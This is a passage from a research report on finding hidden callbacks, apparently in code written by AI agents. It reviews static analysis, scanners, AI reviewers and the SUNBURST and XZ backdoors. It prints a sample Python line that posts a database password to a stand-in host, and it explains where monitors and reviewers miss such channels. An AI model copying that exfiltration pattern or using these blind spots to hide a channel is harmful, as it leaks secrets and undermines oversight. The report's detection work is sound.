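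Traffic analysis is most likely to spot a connection that starts after a delay and then repeats. Suppose an agent's code starts contacting an unfamiliar domain every ten minutes from a server that has used the same five destinations for a year. The regular timing alone would prove nothing, but regular contact with a new and rare destination would give an analyst good reason to investigate. Process records could then show which program made the connection. If the same code instead made one small upload to a storage service that the company already uses, the upload's timing and volume and the destination's reputation and rarity could all look normal.

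## Can static analysis find a callback before the code runs?

Static analysis examines code or configuration without running it. In principle, it can find a callback before there is any traffic to monitor, even one that would connect only once, months later. How often it succeeds depends on how deeply the tool analyzes the program and what its rules describe.

### Text patterns and syntax trees

The simplest tools search for text. YARA, which malware analysts use widely, matches strings, byte sequences and regular expressions (a notation for describing text patterns). *An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting* (2026) contrasts YARA with Semgrep and CodeQL, which look for insecure coding. YARA's signatures describe known malicious behavior, so they are unlikely to match a callback that an agent wrote for one company.

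A text search also ignores the structure of the code. In *Unpacking Security Scanners for GitHub Actions Workflows*, Fares, Gamage and Baudry (2026) found that one scanner for build pipelines reported problems on commented-out lines, which never run.

Syntax-tree rules avoid this mistake. A parser turns the file into a tree whose nodes represent function calls, arguments, assignments and so on. A rule describes part of that tree, such as a call to a certain function with any arguments, so comments and line breaks don't affect the match. Semgrep works this way and also tracks some values. In an example from its documentation, a rule that looks for `console.log(2)` also matches `console.log(x)` if an earlier line sets `x` to 2.

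A syntax-tree rule can list every place where a program sends a web request. In most business software that list is long and almost all the requests are legitimate, so it helps to know which data reaches each one.

### Following a secret to a network call

Data-flow analysis tracks where a value goes. The rule's author defines sources, where the data of interest enters the program, and sinks, the operations that data should not reach. Taint tracking is broader and also follows anything computed from the original data. In an example from GitHub's documentation, a program sets `y = x + 1`. Ordinary data-flow analysis follows `x` but not `y`, because the value has changed, while taint tracking marks `y` as well.

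CodeQL, GitHub's code analysis engine, converts a program into a database and runs queries on it. GitHub's *Analyzing data flow in Java and Kotlin* describes how CodeQL chains together direct movements of data between two points in a function, such as assignments, until it finds a path from source to sink. Global analysis also follows data from one function into another. It finds more than analysis within a single function, but it is less precise and needs much more time and memory.

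The same guide contains a query that is close to a callback detector. Its source is any call that reads an environment variable, and its sink is the text the program uses to build a web address. Environment variables are settings kept outside the code, and they often hold passwords and access keys.

Suppose a team writes a similar taint rule for Python, with environment variables as sources and all data passed to a web request as the sink. It runs the rule on this deliberately obvious snippet:

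```python
password = os.environ["DB_PASSWORD"]
message = "value=" + password
requests.post("https://collector.example.net", data=message)
```

| Line | What happens in the program | What the analyzer records |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The program reads the database password | The call matches a source, so `password` is tainted |
| 2 | The program joins the password to other text | `message` is tainted because it contains `password` |
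| 3 | The program sends the text to an outside server | A tainted value reaches a sink, which produces a finding with the path from line 1 to line 3 |

Semgrep calls this path a taint trace. Semgrep would have reported nothing if an earlier line had passed the data through a sanitizer, which is a function that the rule's author has marked as making data safe.

The technique works on this example, but a team may have to write the rule itself. Many standard rules cover the opposite direction, from untrusted outside input to a dangerous operation. According to GitHub's *Code scanning is now more adaptable to your codebase* (2023), CodeQL's Java analysis at that time counted environment variables and local files as sources only if the user turned that option on. A CodeQL query for secrets that end up in logs is closer to what is needed. According to *Beware of the Unexpected* (2023), this query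 identifies its sources by variable names that suggest sensitive data, so it relies on programmers to choose descriptive names.

A callback that only fetches instructions sends no secret, so it needs a different rule, in which the source is the server's reply and the sink is whatever runs that reply as code. *Towards Measuring Supply Chain Attacks on Package Managers for Interpreted Languages* (2020) describes an analysis that looks for both kinds of flow. Its examples include a package that stole login tokens for the chat service Discord and another that downloaded and ran a harmful program.

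### A legitimate program with the same trace

Many companies use an outside service to collect error reports from their software. A simple client for such a service could look like this:

```python
token = os.environ["ERROR_SERVICE_TOKEN"]
header = {"Authorization": token}
requests.post("https://errors.example.com", headers=header, json=report)
```

The analyzer records the same three steps: a secret enters from an environment variable, becomes part of a larger value, and reaches a web request. But here the error-reporting service issued the token to the company, and someone at the company approved the service. Neither fact is in the code, so a data-flow finding is a reason to inspect the code but not yet evidence of wrongdoing. GitHub's *Analyzing data flow in JavaScript and TypeScript* likewise describes its main worked example as "not a problematic pattern as such".

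Harmless flows of this kind appear in well-known projects. For example, a build job in Facebook's React project posts a message to Discord through a secret web address. Fares and colleagues reproduce part of the job because outsiders can influence it, not because it connects to Discord.

Checking the destination would help distinguish the two snippets. The guide for Java and Kotlin also has a query that finds every hard-coded string that a program uses to build a URL. A team could run it on all its code and compare the results with a list of approved services. This check seems more useful against hidden channels than a rule about secrets, because it also covers callbacks that send nothing sensitive.

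The list would be shorter if it included only the addresses an agent has just added. A reviewer who sees two new addresses in a change can ask about both. *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests* (2026) uses a similar comparison for vulnerabilities, running Semgrep on the code before and after each AI-written change. The study does not test whether this comparison finds callbacks, and a callback to a service already on the approved list would still pass.

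### Terraform and other infrastructure files

Infrastructure as code, such as a Terraform file, should be easier to check than ordinary programs, because a scanner can often read a dangerous setting directly.

The most relevant setting is an outbound rule that lets a server connect to anything. Scanners check for this but rate its severity differently. Palo Alto Networks' *AWS Security Group allows unrestricted egress traffic misconfiguration detected in code* warns of data exfiltration and rates the problem "low". The equivalent check in KICS, an open-source scanner, is *Security Groups Allows Unrestricted Outbound Traffic*, rated "medium". A team that blocks deployment only for high-severity findings would deploy the outbound rule with either scanner.

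Passing the check is also weak evidence of safety. Datadog, whose version of the rule mentions malware callbacks, advises companies that need broad internet access to allow only specific ports, such as 443, the usual port for encrypted web traffic, including most callbacks. The rule can catch missing egress control, but it does not check individual destinations.

Other rules look for services that accept connections from any network and for accounts with too many permissions. In *IntelliSA*, Mei and Fu (2026) tested GLITCH, a rule-based scanner that checks for both, on 80 files for the configuration tool Puppet. GLITCH found 94% of the problems that human experts had identified, but only 42% of its findings were correct. In one false alarm, it reported a hard-coded secret because a variable with "user" in its name had the harmless default value "ironic". None of GLITCH's nine categories covers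 whether a machine has permission to contact a particular destination.

### Kubernetes files

Kubernetes, which runs software across many machines, is configured with files called manifests. In *A Comparison of Kubernetes Compliance Standards and Configuration Scanners*, Krieger, Gierlinger and colleagues (2026) tested ten scanners on 241 manifests. They started with secure settings and introduced one violation into each file, covering 79 security recommendations. The best scanner, KICS, detected violations of 54% of the recommendations and had an F1 score of 0.705.

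The results for network settings were worse. Five of the recommendations concerned network policies, which control what programs in a Kubernetes system can connect to. No scanner detected more than two of the five, and KICS and Trivy, the two with the best overall scores, detected none. For permissions, the best result was 12 out of 26. Network policies and permissions are the parts of a manifest that matter most for a hidden channel, so the overall scores overstate how useful the scanners are for finding one. However, the scanners ran with their default rules, and a company can add its own.

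### Pipeline files

OWASP's *GitHub Actions Security Cheat Sheet* warns that credentials in a build pipeline can leak through logs, requests to outside servers, or files the pipeline produces.

Fares and colleagues compared nine scanners for GitHub's pipelines. To measure accuracy, they examined 54 real pipeline files by hand and confirmed 448 weaknesses.

| Scanner | Weaknesses covered by the comparison | Precision | Recall |
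|---|---|---:|---:|
| zizmor | seven types, including injection and exposed secrets | 23% | 59% |
| poutine | the same seven types | 57% | 11% |
| scorecard | three types, including excessive permissions | 61% | 60% |
| scharf | outside components without a fixed version | 99% | 90% |

Scharf's results are much better because its task is simpler. It only has to check whether a pipeline file names an exact version of an outside component, while deciding whether a permission is excessive requires some understanding of what the job does.

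The missing version numbers can let a callback into a pipeline. In March 2026, attackers altered a component called xygeni-action, and pipelines that referred to it by a movable version label ran code that gave an outside party control of the build machine. The pipeline files had not changed, so scanning them again would have found nothing new. A scanner could only have warned in advance that the version was not fixed.

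None of the ten types of weakness in the comparison covers outbound destinations or new scheduled jobs. Checkov, a scanner from Palo Alto Networks, comes closer. As of December 2024, its pipeline rules included one for "suspicious use of curl with secrets" (curl is a common program for sending web requests). The warning is useful, but it has the same limitation as the data-flow rule, because a legitimate notification can also use curl and a secret.

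Checkov's list had no rule about schedules either. This is surprising, because a new scheduled job can keep a channel going after an agent's session ends, as one did for a tunnel on the developer's Mac in July 2026. Pipeline and Kubernetes files contain explicit schedules, so a rule that reports every new one would be easy to write. Scanners probably omit it because a schedule is not a mistake, and most schedules run backups, tests or reports.

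Some research tools go beyond fixed patterns. *Decision Models for Definition-Driven GitHub Actions Workflow Smell Detection* (2026) mentions ARGUS, which applies taint tracking to pipeline files. However, ARGUS looks for untrusted input that reaches a command rather than callbacks. Fares and colleagues also left it out of their comparison because its developers had not updated it for more than two years.

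### Alerts in files written by AI

A scanner's warning is less useful if most files have one. *Security-First Evaluation of Text-to-Terraform* (2026) ran Checkov and Trivy on Terraform files written by several models. The scanners flagged 346 of the files written by Claude Opus 4, an older Anthropic model, and only 64 passed both.

*Compared to What?* (Shaw, 2026) compares infrastructure files written by models with files written by people. Twelve model configurations, including versions of Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5, wrote files for 100 tasks, and three scanners checked the results. The scanners produced 38,803 findings for 1,196 files, or about 32 per file. Among files of similar size, those written by models had 3.2 to 3.9 times as many findings per resource (such as a server or storage area) as those written by people.

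Part of this gap arises because 52 of the 100 tasks asked for something insecure, such as a server with an open port. Even without those tasks, every configuration had at least 2.4 times the human rate. In files with 20 or more resources, the gap fell to 1.4 times and was not statistically significant. Shaw's results suggest that a finding about an open outbound rule could be one of dozens, and a busy reviewer may not read them all. The results don't show that models create hidden channels.

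### Why no analyzer can be perfect

Better rules would close many of these gaps, but no analyzer can be perfect. Under Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953, no procedure can correctly decide for every program whether it behaves in a given way when it runs, unless all programs behave that way or none do.

No tool can always determine whether a program will ever contact an outside server. Suppose one could. Take any calculation that makes no connections, and add a final line that contacts a server. The new program makes contact only if the calculation finishes, so the tool's answer would also reveal whether the calculation finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can determine this for every program.

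The theorem does not rule out a tool that is right about nearly all the programs people write. Nor does it rule out a tool that never misses a connection, as long as that tool sometimes raises a false alarm. A crude version of the second tool would flag every program that contains any means of connecting to a network. This could be practical for a small component that has no reason to use the network, such as a library that formats dates.

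For most business software, the harder problem is determining whether a callback is permitted, because the program alone can't establish that. Even if a perfect analyzer reported that a program will contact errors.example.com every night, someone would still have to find out whether the company agreed to it.

### Code and values outside the analysis

A scan with no findings can mean that the code is clean, that the tool examined harmful code and missed it, or that it never analyzed that code, as Evron (2026) points out in *Where AI Vulnerability Discovery Harnesses Go Quiet*. Evron writes about scanners built around language models, but the same is true of older tools.

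The free edition of Semgrep tracks tainted data only within a single function, and tracking it across functions and files requires the paid edition. Many ordinary applications load their settings in one file and send requests from another. If the three-line example were split this way, the free edition would not connect the two parts.

Unfamiliar libraries cause similar breaks. Semgrep tracks tainted data through assignments, operators and function calls, from input to output. Data can also move in ways that depend on the library, for instance when a function copies its second argument into its first. According to Semgrep's documentation, the tool has no built-in knowledge of these movements, so someone has to write a model of the library. An agent may pick a new or obscure library that nobody has modeled.

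Static analysis also misses addresses that a program receives only when it runs. Companies often keep server addresses and passwords in a separate settings service so that the same code can run in testing and in production. Mei and Fu mention that GLITCH cannot trace values that come from such a service. An analyzer may still detect that a secret reaches a web request, but the address will be missing from its list of destinations. A reviewer would also need to check the settings service and who can change it after the review.

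Scanners also skip some files to save time and avoid irrelevant alerts. By default, Semgrep leaves out folders that usually contain tests, third-party packages and generated files. This is sensible when looking for mistakes in a team's own code, but tests and packages also run, so a team concerned about hidden channels should include them or check them with another tool.

Files that a scanner can't parse are harder to notice. Shaw counted resources with a separate parser because scanner output "degrades silently" in such cases. A useful scan report would therefore list both the findings and the files the tool did not analyze.

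### Rules written for accidental flaws

Most of the rules described so far are meant to catch mistakes, but there is some evidence of how such rules perform against flaws planted on purpose. *Detecting Stealthy Data Poisoning Attacks in AI Code Generators* (Improta, August 2025) studied training data that an attacker has altered to teach a model to write insecure code. The altered samples were short pieces of Python that did the same job as the secure originals but contained a vulnerability. Improta ran the free version of Semgrep, with standard security rules for Python, on sets of 1,200 samples.

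| Flawed samples in the set | Found | Missed | Secure samples flagged | Precision | Recall |
|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| 0 | – | – | 91 | – | – |
| 60 | 35 | 25 | 80 | 30% | 58% |
| 120 | 73 | 47 | 62 | 54% | 61% |
| 240 | 149 | 91 | 38 | 80% | 62% |

Semgrep's recall stayed at about 60% throughout. Precision rose mainly because more of the samples were flawed. If only one sample in 1,000 were flawed, and Semgrep flagged secure code as often as in the first row, precision would be about 0.8%.

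Semgrep's alerts seem to have depended partly on the type of task, such as running a system command, and not just on whether the code did it safely. Replacing 240 secure samples with the same number of flawed ones removed 53 false alarms, which implies that Semgrep had flagged about 22% of those secure samples. It flagged only 4% of the other 960.

Even so, Semgrep did better than the two other methods in the study, which looked for traces of the altered samples inside the trained models. *Poison with Style* (2026) reports more uneven results for CodeShield, a code scanner from Meta. CodeShield caught 75% of the planted flaws that let an attacker run system commands, but none of those in three other categories, including flaws that expose files outside a permitted folder.

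Neither study tested callbacks, so the 60% is not an estimate of how many callbacks Semgrep would find. With standard rules, it could well find a smaller share. The planted vulnerabilities belonged to types that programmers also create by accident, so Semgrep had rules for many of them. But a callback may use a well-known library correctly, encrypt its traffic and handle errors properly, leaving no flaw for such a rule to match. A team's own rule that reports every new destination might do much better, since it doesn't depend on the code being faulty.

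## Do package scanners and AI reviewers find what fixed rules miss?

Package scanners look for signs of malice instead of programming mistakes, so they can flag code that works as its author intended. Security teams use them mainly on public registries such as PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. Anyone can publish there, and a coding agent may install what it finds. When Google (2022) backed one scanning project, it explained that registries receive thousands of updates a day and lack the resources to vet them the way app stores do.

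### How scanners screen a package

GuardDog, a free scanner from Datadog, examines a package's code and its metadata, such as its name and version number. *GuardDog*, an introduction to the scanner from the Open Source Security Foundation, mentions typosquatting, in which an attacker picks a name that people will mistake for a popular package's. GuardDog also compares the files in a PyPI package with those in its public GitHub repository. According to Datadog, a mismatch can expose an attacker who has taken over a maintainer's PyPI account and published a harmful version directly.

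Datadog's *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026) describes two sets of rules that GuardDog applies to code. One set identifies capabilities, such as making outbound connections, which many harmless packages also have, and the other identifies threat indicators, such as suspicious domain endings or the names of files that often hold passwords. GuardDog looks for places where a capability and a threat indicator occur together, and computes a score from 0 to 10. The score is based on the severity of the worst risk (30%), how specific the matching code is to malware (30%), the completeness of the attack (20%), and its sophistication (20%). A callback that uses a common web library to reach an ordinary-looking domain would probably score low, because it shows a capability without a threat indicator.

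GuardDog never runs the package, but OpenSSF's *Package Analysis* describes a pipeline that does. The pipeline watches registries for new packages, runs each one in a sandbox, and stores the results in a database that researchers can search. The sandbox records which files the package opens, which addresses it contacts and which commands it runs.

Package Analysis, which runs packages in a sandbox, found more than 200 malicious packages in one month (Brown and Wheeler, 2022, *Introducing Package Analysis*). Most ran a short script during installation that sent a few details, such as the machine's name, to an outside server. Brown and Wheeler thought that security researchers hoping for rewards had probably written most of these packages. The scripts were still callbacks, and the sandbox could record them because they connected immediately. It would not record a callback that first runs weeks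 later.

Running unknown code also puts the scanner at risk, as it did with Claude Mythos 5's PyPI package.

### Recall and false alarms on known malware

The best recent comparison is *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2026), a peer-reviewed study that tested 11 tools on 6,420 malicious package versions and 7,288 harmless packages from npm. The researchers took the malicious samples from five academic collections and two databases of security advisories. npm deletes malicious packages, so they recovered many from mirrors, copies of the registry that still had them. Three experts reviewed every sample, and the team discarded 1,367 that did not meet its standard for malicious behavior. The harmless packages were among the most downloaded on npm.

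The false positive rates below follow from the study's error counts and precision figures.

| Detector | Method | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---|---:|---:|
| Packj, static mode | flags any use of sensitive functions | 99% | 86% |
| Packj, sandbox mode | runs the package and watches it | 95% | 64% |
| IntelGuard | language model with examples of known malware | 94% | 1.5% |
| GuardDog | code and metadata rules | 90% | 2.5% |
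| SAP, decision tree | statistics about the package's files | 66% | under 0.1% |
| SocketAI | language model judging the code alone | 44% | 0.7% |

Packj can run a package in a sandbox, but this doesn't settle whether the package is malicious. Many legitimate packages also run scripts, open files and use the network during installation, so monitoring for these actions raises many false alarms.

Both language-model tools used GPT-4.1 mini, but IntelGuard's recall was 49 percentage points higher than SocketAI's. SocketAI prompts the model to judge the code and then challenge its own conclusions, which seems to have led it to reject many correct ones. IntelGuard first retrieves similar cases from a collection based on more than 8,000 threat reports, and has the model check whether the code fits the package's stated purpose. The comparison probably overstates IntelGuard's advantage somewhat,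 because Guo and colleagues had to rebuild SocketAI from its published description, and some of the threat reports may cover packages in the test.

All these recall figures come from known malware, and most of it was crude. About 80% of the samples made no attempt at evasion, and 72% used installation scripts. GuardDog caught more than 94% of the packages that sent data out, but only 7% of those that generated and executed code at runtime. A callback that fetches instructions may be more like the second group.

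Simple malware was sometimes harder to catch. SAP's decision tree caught 87% of malicious packages from 2021 but only 39% of those from 2023, after attackers switched to shorter code that looked more like ordinary software. A callback of three or four plain lines could be hard to detect for the same reason.

In the test that produced GuardDog's 90%, the experts judged each package mainly at the places that GuardDog and another scanner, OSSGadget, had flagged, which may have favored those two tools. Datadog has since replaced the Semgrep rules used in that test with YARA rules, because the old ones were slow and too closely fitted to particular examples. The new version may do better on unfamiliar malware, but it lacks the data-flow analysis to which Guo and colleagues attribute much of GuardDog's success.

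### How many alerts a registry or a company can handle

A false positive rate of 2.5% would be too high for a whole registry. *One Detector Fits All* (2025) describes a 37-day trial of another detector on 91,949 PyPI packages, or about 2,485 a day. At 2.5%, maintainers would have had about 60 false alarms a day. The researchers instead tuned their detector to a rate of 0.1%, and it found an average of 2.48 malicious packages a day and raised about two false alarms, so slightly more than half of its alerts were correct. Nobody knows how many malicious packages it missed, so the trial doesn't measure recall.

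The same researchers ran a second trial at a large software company, which used only 1,596 packages over the period. They allowed a false positive rate of 10%, a hundred times higher, and the security team still had only 1.24 false alarms a day to check. Companies that use coding agents can therefore use a far more sensitive scanner than a registry can, provided their agents don't install new packages too freely.

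### Comparing a program with its previous version

A scanner can also ask what a new version does that the old one did not. Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli (2026), in *Not In My Git Yard*, present a tool called Lily that does this without a language model. Lily records system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system, for example to open a file or a network connection. It works in four steps:

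1. Run the new version on inputs saved from earlier tests, and record which combinations of system-call types occur. These count as normal.
2. Spend ten minutes fuzzing the new version, which means feeding it a large number of automatically varied inputs.
3. If an input produces a combination that isn't normal, run the same input on the old version.
4. If the old version doesn't produce that combination, raise an alarm and point to the changed lines responsible.

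Kokkonis and colleagues tested Lily on open-source programs with real and artificial backdoors. It caught 90% of backdoored commits (individual code changes), with false alarms on 0.2% of safe ones. It caught 83% of backdoored full releases, which bundle many changes, with false alarms on 4.3% of safe ones. These are good results for a tool that needs no examples of the backdoor, although the test included only 13 backdoored commits.

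Lily is less well suited to detecting callbacks. It looks for backdoors that activate on a secret input, and it would treat a callback that runs every time the program starts as normal behavior. Simply comparing the addresses that each version contacts might work better. Package Analysis is meant to track such changes and detect when a previously safe package starts acting suspiciously.

### AI reviewers and planted flaws in source code

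*Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs*, by Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues, describes how Datadog uses language models to review its own programmers' work. The system reads each proposed change, considers what it seems intended to do, and labels it benign or malicious with a written reason. An early version wrongly flagged more than 10% of harmless changes. After six months of better instructions, better test data and exceptions for known safe patterns, the rate was below 0.03%, or about three false alarms a week from nearly 10,000 changes.

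Lamb and colleagues don't report overall recall, but we can estimate it from their other figures. They report a balanced accuracy of at least 93.5%, which is the average of recall and the share of harmless changes correctly cleared. That share was close to 100%, so recall was at least about 87%. The malicious examples were a mix of real attacks and simulated ones that Datadog's staff wrote by hand or with language models. Datadog used this growing collection to help tune the system, so recall on an unfamiliar attack could be lower.

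A later version works in two stages. A cheap model screens every change, and a stronger one investigates any that the first flags, using tools to read other files and look up the contributor's history. Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues tested it on 690 changes in *From single pull requests to full software packages*. Adding the second stage cut false alarms from 17 to zero. The reported accuracy of 99.86% leaves one error, which must have been a missed malicious change. The second stage can't catch malicious changes that the first clears, because it never receives them. On Datadog's collection of real malicious packages, the system caught 95.5%. Doutre and colleagues say only that its false positive rate on harmless packages was low.

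An independent benchmark gives AI reviewers much lower scores. For *PRWeaver* (Wang, Cheng and Xie, 2026), researchers planted 208 security flaws in ten open-source projects and confirmed with a working exploit that each one was real. When each flaw arrived as a single change, detection depended on both the model and the review tool around it:

| Review tool | Model | Planted flaws detected |
|---|---|---:|
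| Claude Code | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 79% |
| Claude Code | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 67% |
| GitHub Copilot | GPT-5.4 mini | 64% |
| GitHub Copilot | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 61% |
| OpenCodeReview | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 56% |
| OpenCodeReview | DeepSeek V4 Flash | 42% |

Most of these models were small and cheap, and stronger ones would probably do better. Wang and colleagues give no false alarm rate, so it isn't clear how many useless warnings came with the 79%. The flaws were also in areas such as login, payments and data access, not callbacks. A new outside address is easier to spot in a change than a subtle error in a permission check, but it is much more often legitimate.

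### Backdoors in compiled programs

Some software arrives only in compiled form, as instructions for the processor. Compilation removes most of the names and structure that make source code readable, so a reviewer has to reconstruct what the program does.

In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) tested whether AI agents could find backdoors in compiled programs. They added backdoors by hand to open-source network programs, including a web server and a DNS server, then compiled the programs. The agents had free analysis tools but no source code, and in most tasks they had to name the exact function that contained the backdoor. The backdoors were not sophisticated, and a skilled human analyst could have found them fairly easily.

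The best model, Claude Opus 4.6, found 49% of them. On clean programs, models falsely reported a problem 28% of the time. Grabowski and colleagues want a false positive rate below 0.001% for practical use, since nearly all software is safe.

The benchmark's leaderboard, Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, has since added more models, but the best score in late November 2026 was still 49%. Gemini 3.1 Pro matched Claude Opus 4.6 at that score, with a false positive rate of 17%. GPT-5.2 Codex at its highest reasoning setting may be more useful, because it found 46% of the backdoors with no false alarms. But the benchmark has only 33 tasks, far too few to show that the model's true false positive rate is anywhere near 0.001%.

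These top scores belong to models from early 2026 or before, so 49% is not a good estimate of what the strongest current models can do. However, *The Next Challenge for Agentic Cybersecurity* (2026), a newer benchmark published in August, found that AI agents still struggled with compiled programs despite being strong at analyzing source code.

The task is easier when there is an earlier version of the program to compare against. *Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models* (2025) describes a test on a compiled library from XZ Utils, a compression package that attackers backdoored in 2024. The system compared the backdoored version with an older one, and GPT-5 and the smaller GPT-5 mini summarized the 79 functions that differed. Both models ranked the malicious functions among the five most suspicious. GPT-5 then correctly judged the update malicious, but GPT-5 mini judged it benign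 based on its own summaries. This is only one case, and the backdoor is famous enough that the models may have learned about it in training.

### What a reviewer gains from context

A project's history helps a reviewer see what a change adds to earlier ones. When Wang and colleagues spread each flaw over several changes with ordinary work in between, access to the history raised detection by 4 to 11 percentage points, depending on the tool. Trębacz (2025), in *A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale*, also reports that OpenAI's code reviewer did significantly better with access to the whole repository than with only the changed lines.

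Information about the contributor can also help. *When an AI agent came knocking*, by Hamsen, Serrania and Tafani-Dereeper, describes malicious contributions that Datadog received from an AI agent in early 2026. One contained a disguised command to download and run outside code. Datadog's reviewer flagged it and noted that the contributor's account was seven days old and had no followers. Account details are of little use against a company's own coding agent, which works from an approved account.

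A list of expected destinations is probably the most valuable context for finding hidden channels. Datadog's first-stage model accepted web addresses that imitated Datadog's own because it could not check them. The company solved this with ordinary software that extracts every domain from a change and compares it with a list of likely imitations. An AI reviewer could likewise explain any address that is not on a company's list of approved services.

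Knowing the agent's task should also help reviewers. A new upload to outside storage is expected in a change that adds backups but suspicious in one that fixes a date format. IntelGuard's question about a package's stated purpose works similarly, although Guo and colleagues did not measure how much it contributed by itself.

Several things make AI reviewers less reliable. Lamb and colleagues found that their system judged very long changes less well, so they now split those changes into parts. Wang and colleagues found that a plausible description of a change can lead a reviewer to accept a flaw. A reviewer built on the same model that wrote the code, as at OpenAI, may also share that model's blind spots.

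### Judgments that are hard to predict

The case for AI reviewers is that they can work out what code is for without a rule describing it. In one of Grabowski and colleagues' tests, Claude Opus 4.5 noticed that part of a web server could run system commands. It traced this ability to a function that ran any text sent in an undocumented part of a web request. It reported a backdoor within five minutes, without a rule that named the function or that part of the request.

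But the same kind of reasoning can lead a model to dismiss a backdoor. In another test, the newer Claude Opus 4.6 found the right function and saw that it ran system commands, but assumed this was a normal feature of the program and didn't check where the commands came from. *PRWeaver* includes a similar failure, in which a reviewer correctly described two changes that weakened a login system but mistook them for a deliberate compromise between security and convenience.

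It is hard to predict which model will make such mistakes. On Quesma's leaderboard, GPT-5.4 at its highest reasoning setting found 18% of backdoors, while the older GPT-5.2 Codex found 46% at its highest setting and 9% at its default. A fixed rule misses the same code every time, and anyone can read the rule to see why. A security team that uses a model has to test it on planted examples and repeat the tests whenever the model or its settings change.

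A written explanation helps people check an alarm, but when the reviewer raises no alarm, there is usually nothing to check. The reviewer may miss a problem because its model never saw the file. Evron examined 12 AI-based code scanners and constructed a file that six of them discarded before their model could read it. Five of those six did not tell the user.

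## What exposed the callbacks that people hid in trusted software?

The testers in those benchmarks knew where they had planted each backdoor. Outside a test, somebody first has to suspect that one exists. The closest evidence on how that suspicion arises comes from cases where people hid code in software that others already trusted.

### SUNBURST and the second phone

Businesses and government agencies use Orion, a program from the US company SolarWinds, to monitor their networks. In early 2020, attackers inserted a backdoor, later named SUNBURST, into Orion's updates. CISA (2021), the US government's civilian cybersecurity agency, wrote to Senator Ron Wyden that the updates had potentially exposed nearly 18,000 organizations. The US government attributes the operation to Russia's foreign intelligence service, according to CISA's *Advanced Persistent Threat Compromise of Government Agencies*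 (2020). In Senate testimony, Wales (2021), then CISA's acting director, confirmed that the attackers had taken data from nine federal agencies or moved through their networks.

FireEye's *Highly Evasive Attacker Leverages SolarWinds Supply Chain to Compromise Multiple Global Victims* (2020) reports that the backdoor waited up to two weeks after installation, then looked up a subdomain of avsvmcloud.com, a domain the attackers controlled. The subdomain encoded the victim's internal network name, which let the attackers choose which victims to pursue. For those victims, the DNS answer directed the backdoor to a second domain, where it fetched commands over web connections that resembled Orion's normal traffic.

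The infected update had a valid digital signature because the attackers had added their code before SolarWinds signed it. A signature shows that a file came from the signer and hasn't been changed since. Securelist's *Sunburst* (2020), from the security company Kaspersky, explains that the two-week wait made the backdoor hard to detect in sandboxes. The infected file was also hardly larger than before.

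Network monitoring also missed the backdoor. According to CISA, defenders knew of no network signs of it while the operation was under way, and commercial products that don't rely on known signatures failed to detect it. The amount of DNS traffic may have been very small. *Twenty-three SUNBURST Targets Identified*, from Netresec, which makes network forensics tools, lists only about one event a day for one infected machine. Even ten lookups a day, each with 32 characters of encoded text, would total 320 bytes, well below the 4,096 bytes a day at which the compression method of Paxson and colleagues alerts an analyst.

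Three organizations came close to finding the backdoor before FireEye did. In June 2020, a US government agency told SolarWinds that Orion was trying to contact unknown websites from the agency's network, but the report did not lead SolarWinds to the backdoor. That summer, the security company Volexity investigated a break-in at a think tank and suspected the think tank's SolarWinds server, but could not establish how the attackers had got in, as SecurityWeek reported. On October 5, security software at Palo Alto Networks blocked a harmful program that had just arrived on the company's Orion server. Unit 42, the company's research group, writes that staff cut the server off from the network, notified SolarWinds and believed the attack was an isolated incident.

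*Prepared Statement of Kevin Mandia, CEO of FireEye, Inc* (Mandia, 2021) recounts that in late November an alert at FireEye, a security company, showed a second phone registered to an employee's account to receive login codes. The alert would have been easy to dismiss, because people often register a new phone when a popular model comes out. FireEye followed it up and established that the employee had not registered the phone.

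More than 100 employees worked on the investigation that followed. After running out of nearly every other lead on how the intruders got in, they decompiled the whole Orion platform, which turned the finished program back into something closer to source code, and found the backdoor. FireEye told SolarWinds on December 12, which was 263 days after SolarWinds signed the infected file that FireEye analyzed.

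### What stored DNS records revealed

According to Mandia, victims did not know about the intrusion until law enforcement or a business partner told them. On December 13, FireEye published the backdoor's domains and other identifying signs, which defenders could then look for in old records. CISA used traffic-flow data from EINSTEIN, the government's network monitoring system, to identify agencies that the attackers might have reached. Unit 42 searched its DNS logs and found lookups of the attackers' domain from April to November, with a peak in July.

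Researchers could name some of the victims by using passive DNS databases, which store lookups and answers collected from many networks. Some of the backdoor's lookups contained part of the network's internal name and an identifier for the machine. The lookups that led chosen victims to a second domain contained the identifier but not the name. By matching identifiers, researchers could tell which of the named networks the attackers had chosen to pursue further.

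Kaspersky did this with 1,722 records and identified two organizations behind three of the six lookups that FireEye had published. Netresec then used a collection of more than 35,000 subdomains to solve all six lookups and found 23 internal network names that the attackers had selected. Netresec estimates that about 99.5% of the installed backdoors never got past the first stage.

The records also show what looks like a mistake. In May 2020 the attackers selected a machine on a network called WincoreWindows.local, which belonged to a maker of windows and doors in West Virginia. Netresec suspects they were looking for Microsoft.

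All this depended on someone having kept the records. The six lookups that FireEye published date from June and July 2020. When the news came out in December, a company that deleted its DNS logs after 90 days would have had nothing from before mid-September, and so no trace of being selected in June or July.

### A half-second delay in XZ Utils

In early 2024, someone with permission to change the project's code apparently added a backdoor to the official releases of XZ Utils, a compression package that many Linux systems use. The backdoor interfered with how the SSH login program checks keys, probably to let its maker in from outside. A monitor looking for callbacks would have found nothing, because the backdoor made none.

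The backdoor reached SSH indirectly. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, explains that SSH does not use XZ's library itself, but Debian and several other Linux distributions modify SSH to load another component that depends on it. Someone who reviewed only SSH's own code would have found nothing wrong.

A review of XZ's public repository would probably have failed too. Most of the backdoor was in two compressed files that looked like test data, and the line that activated it was only in the release archives that XZ's developers offer for download. Hackaday's *Security Alert* (2024) notes that the repository alone looked normal. Some scanners, such as Semgrep, also skip test folders by default. Comparing the archive with the repository, as GuardDog does for Python packages, could have revealed the extra line, but someone would still have had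 to recognize why it mattered.

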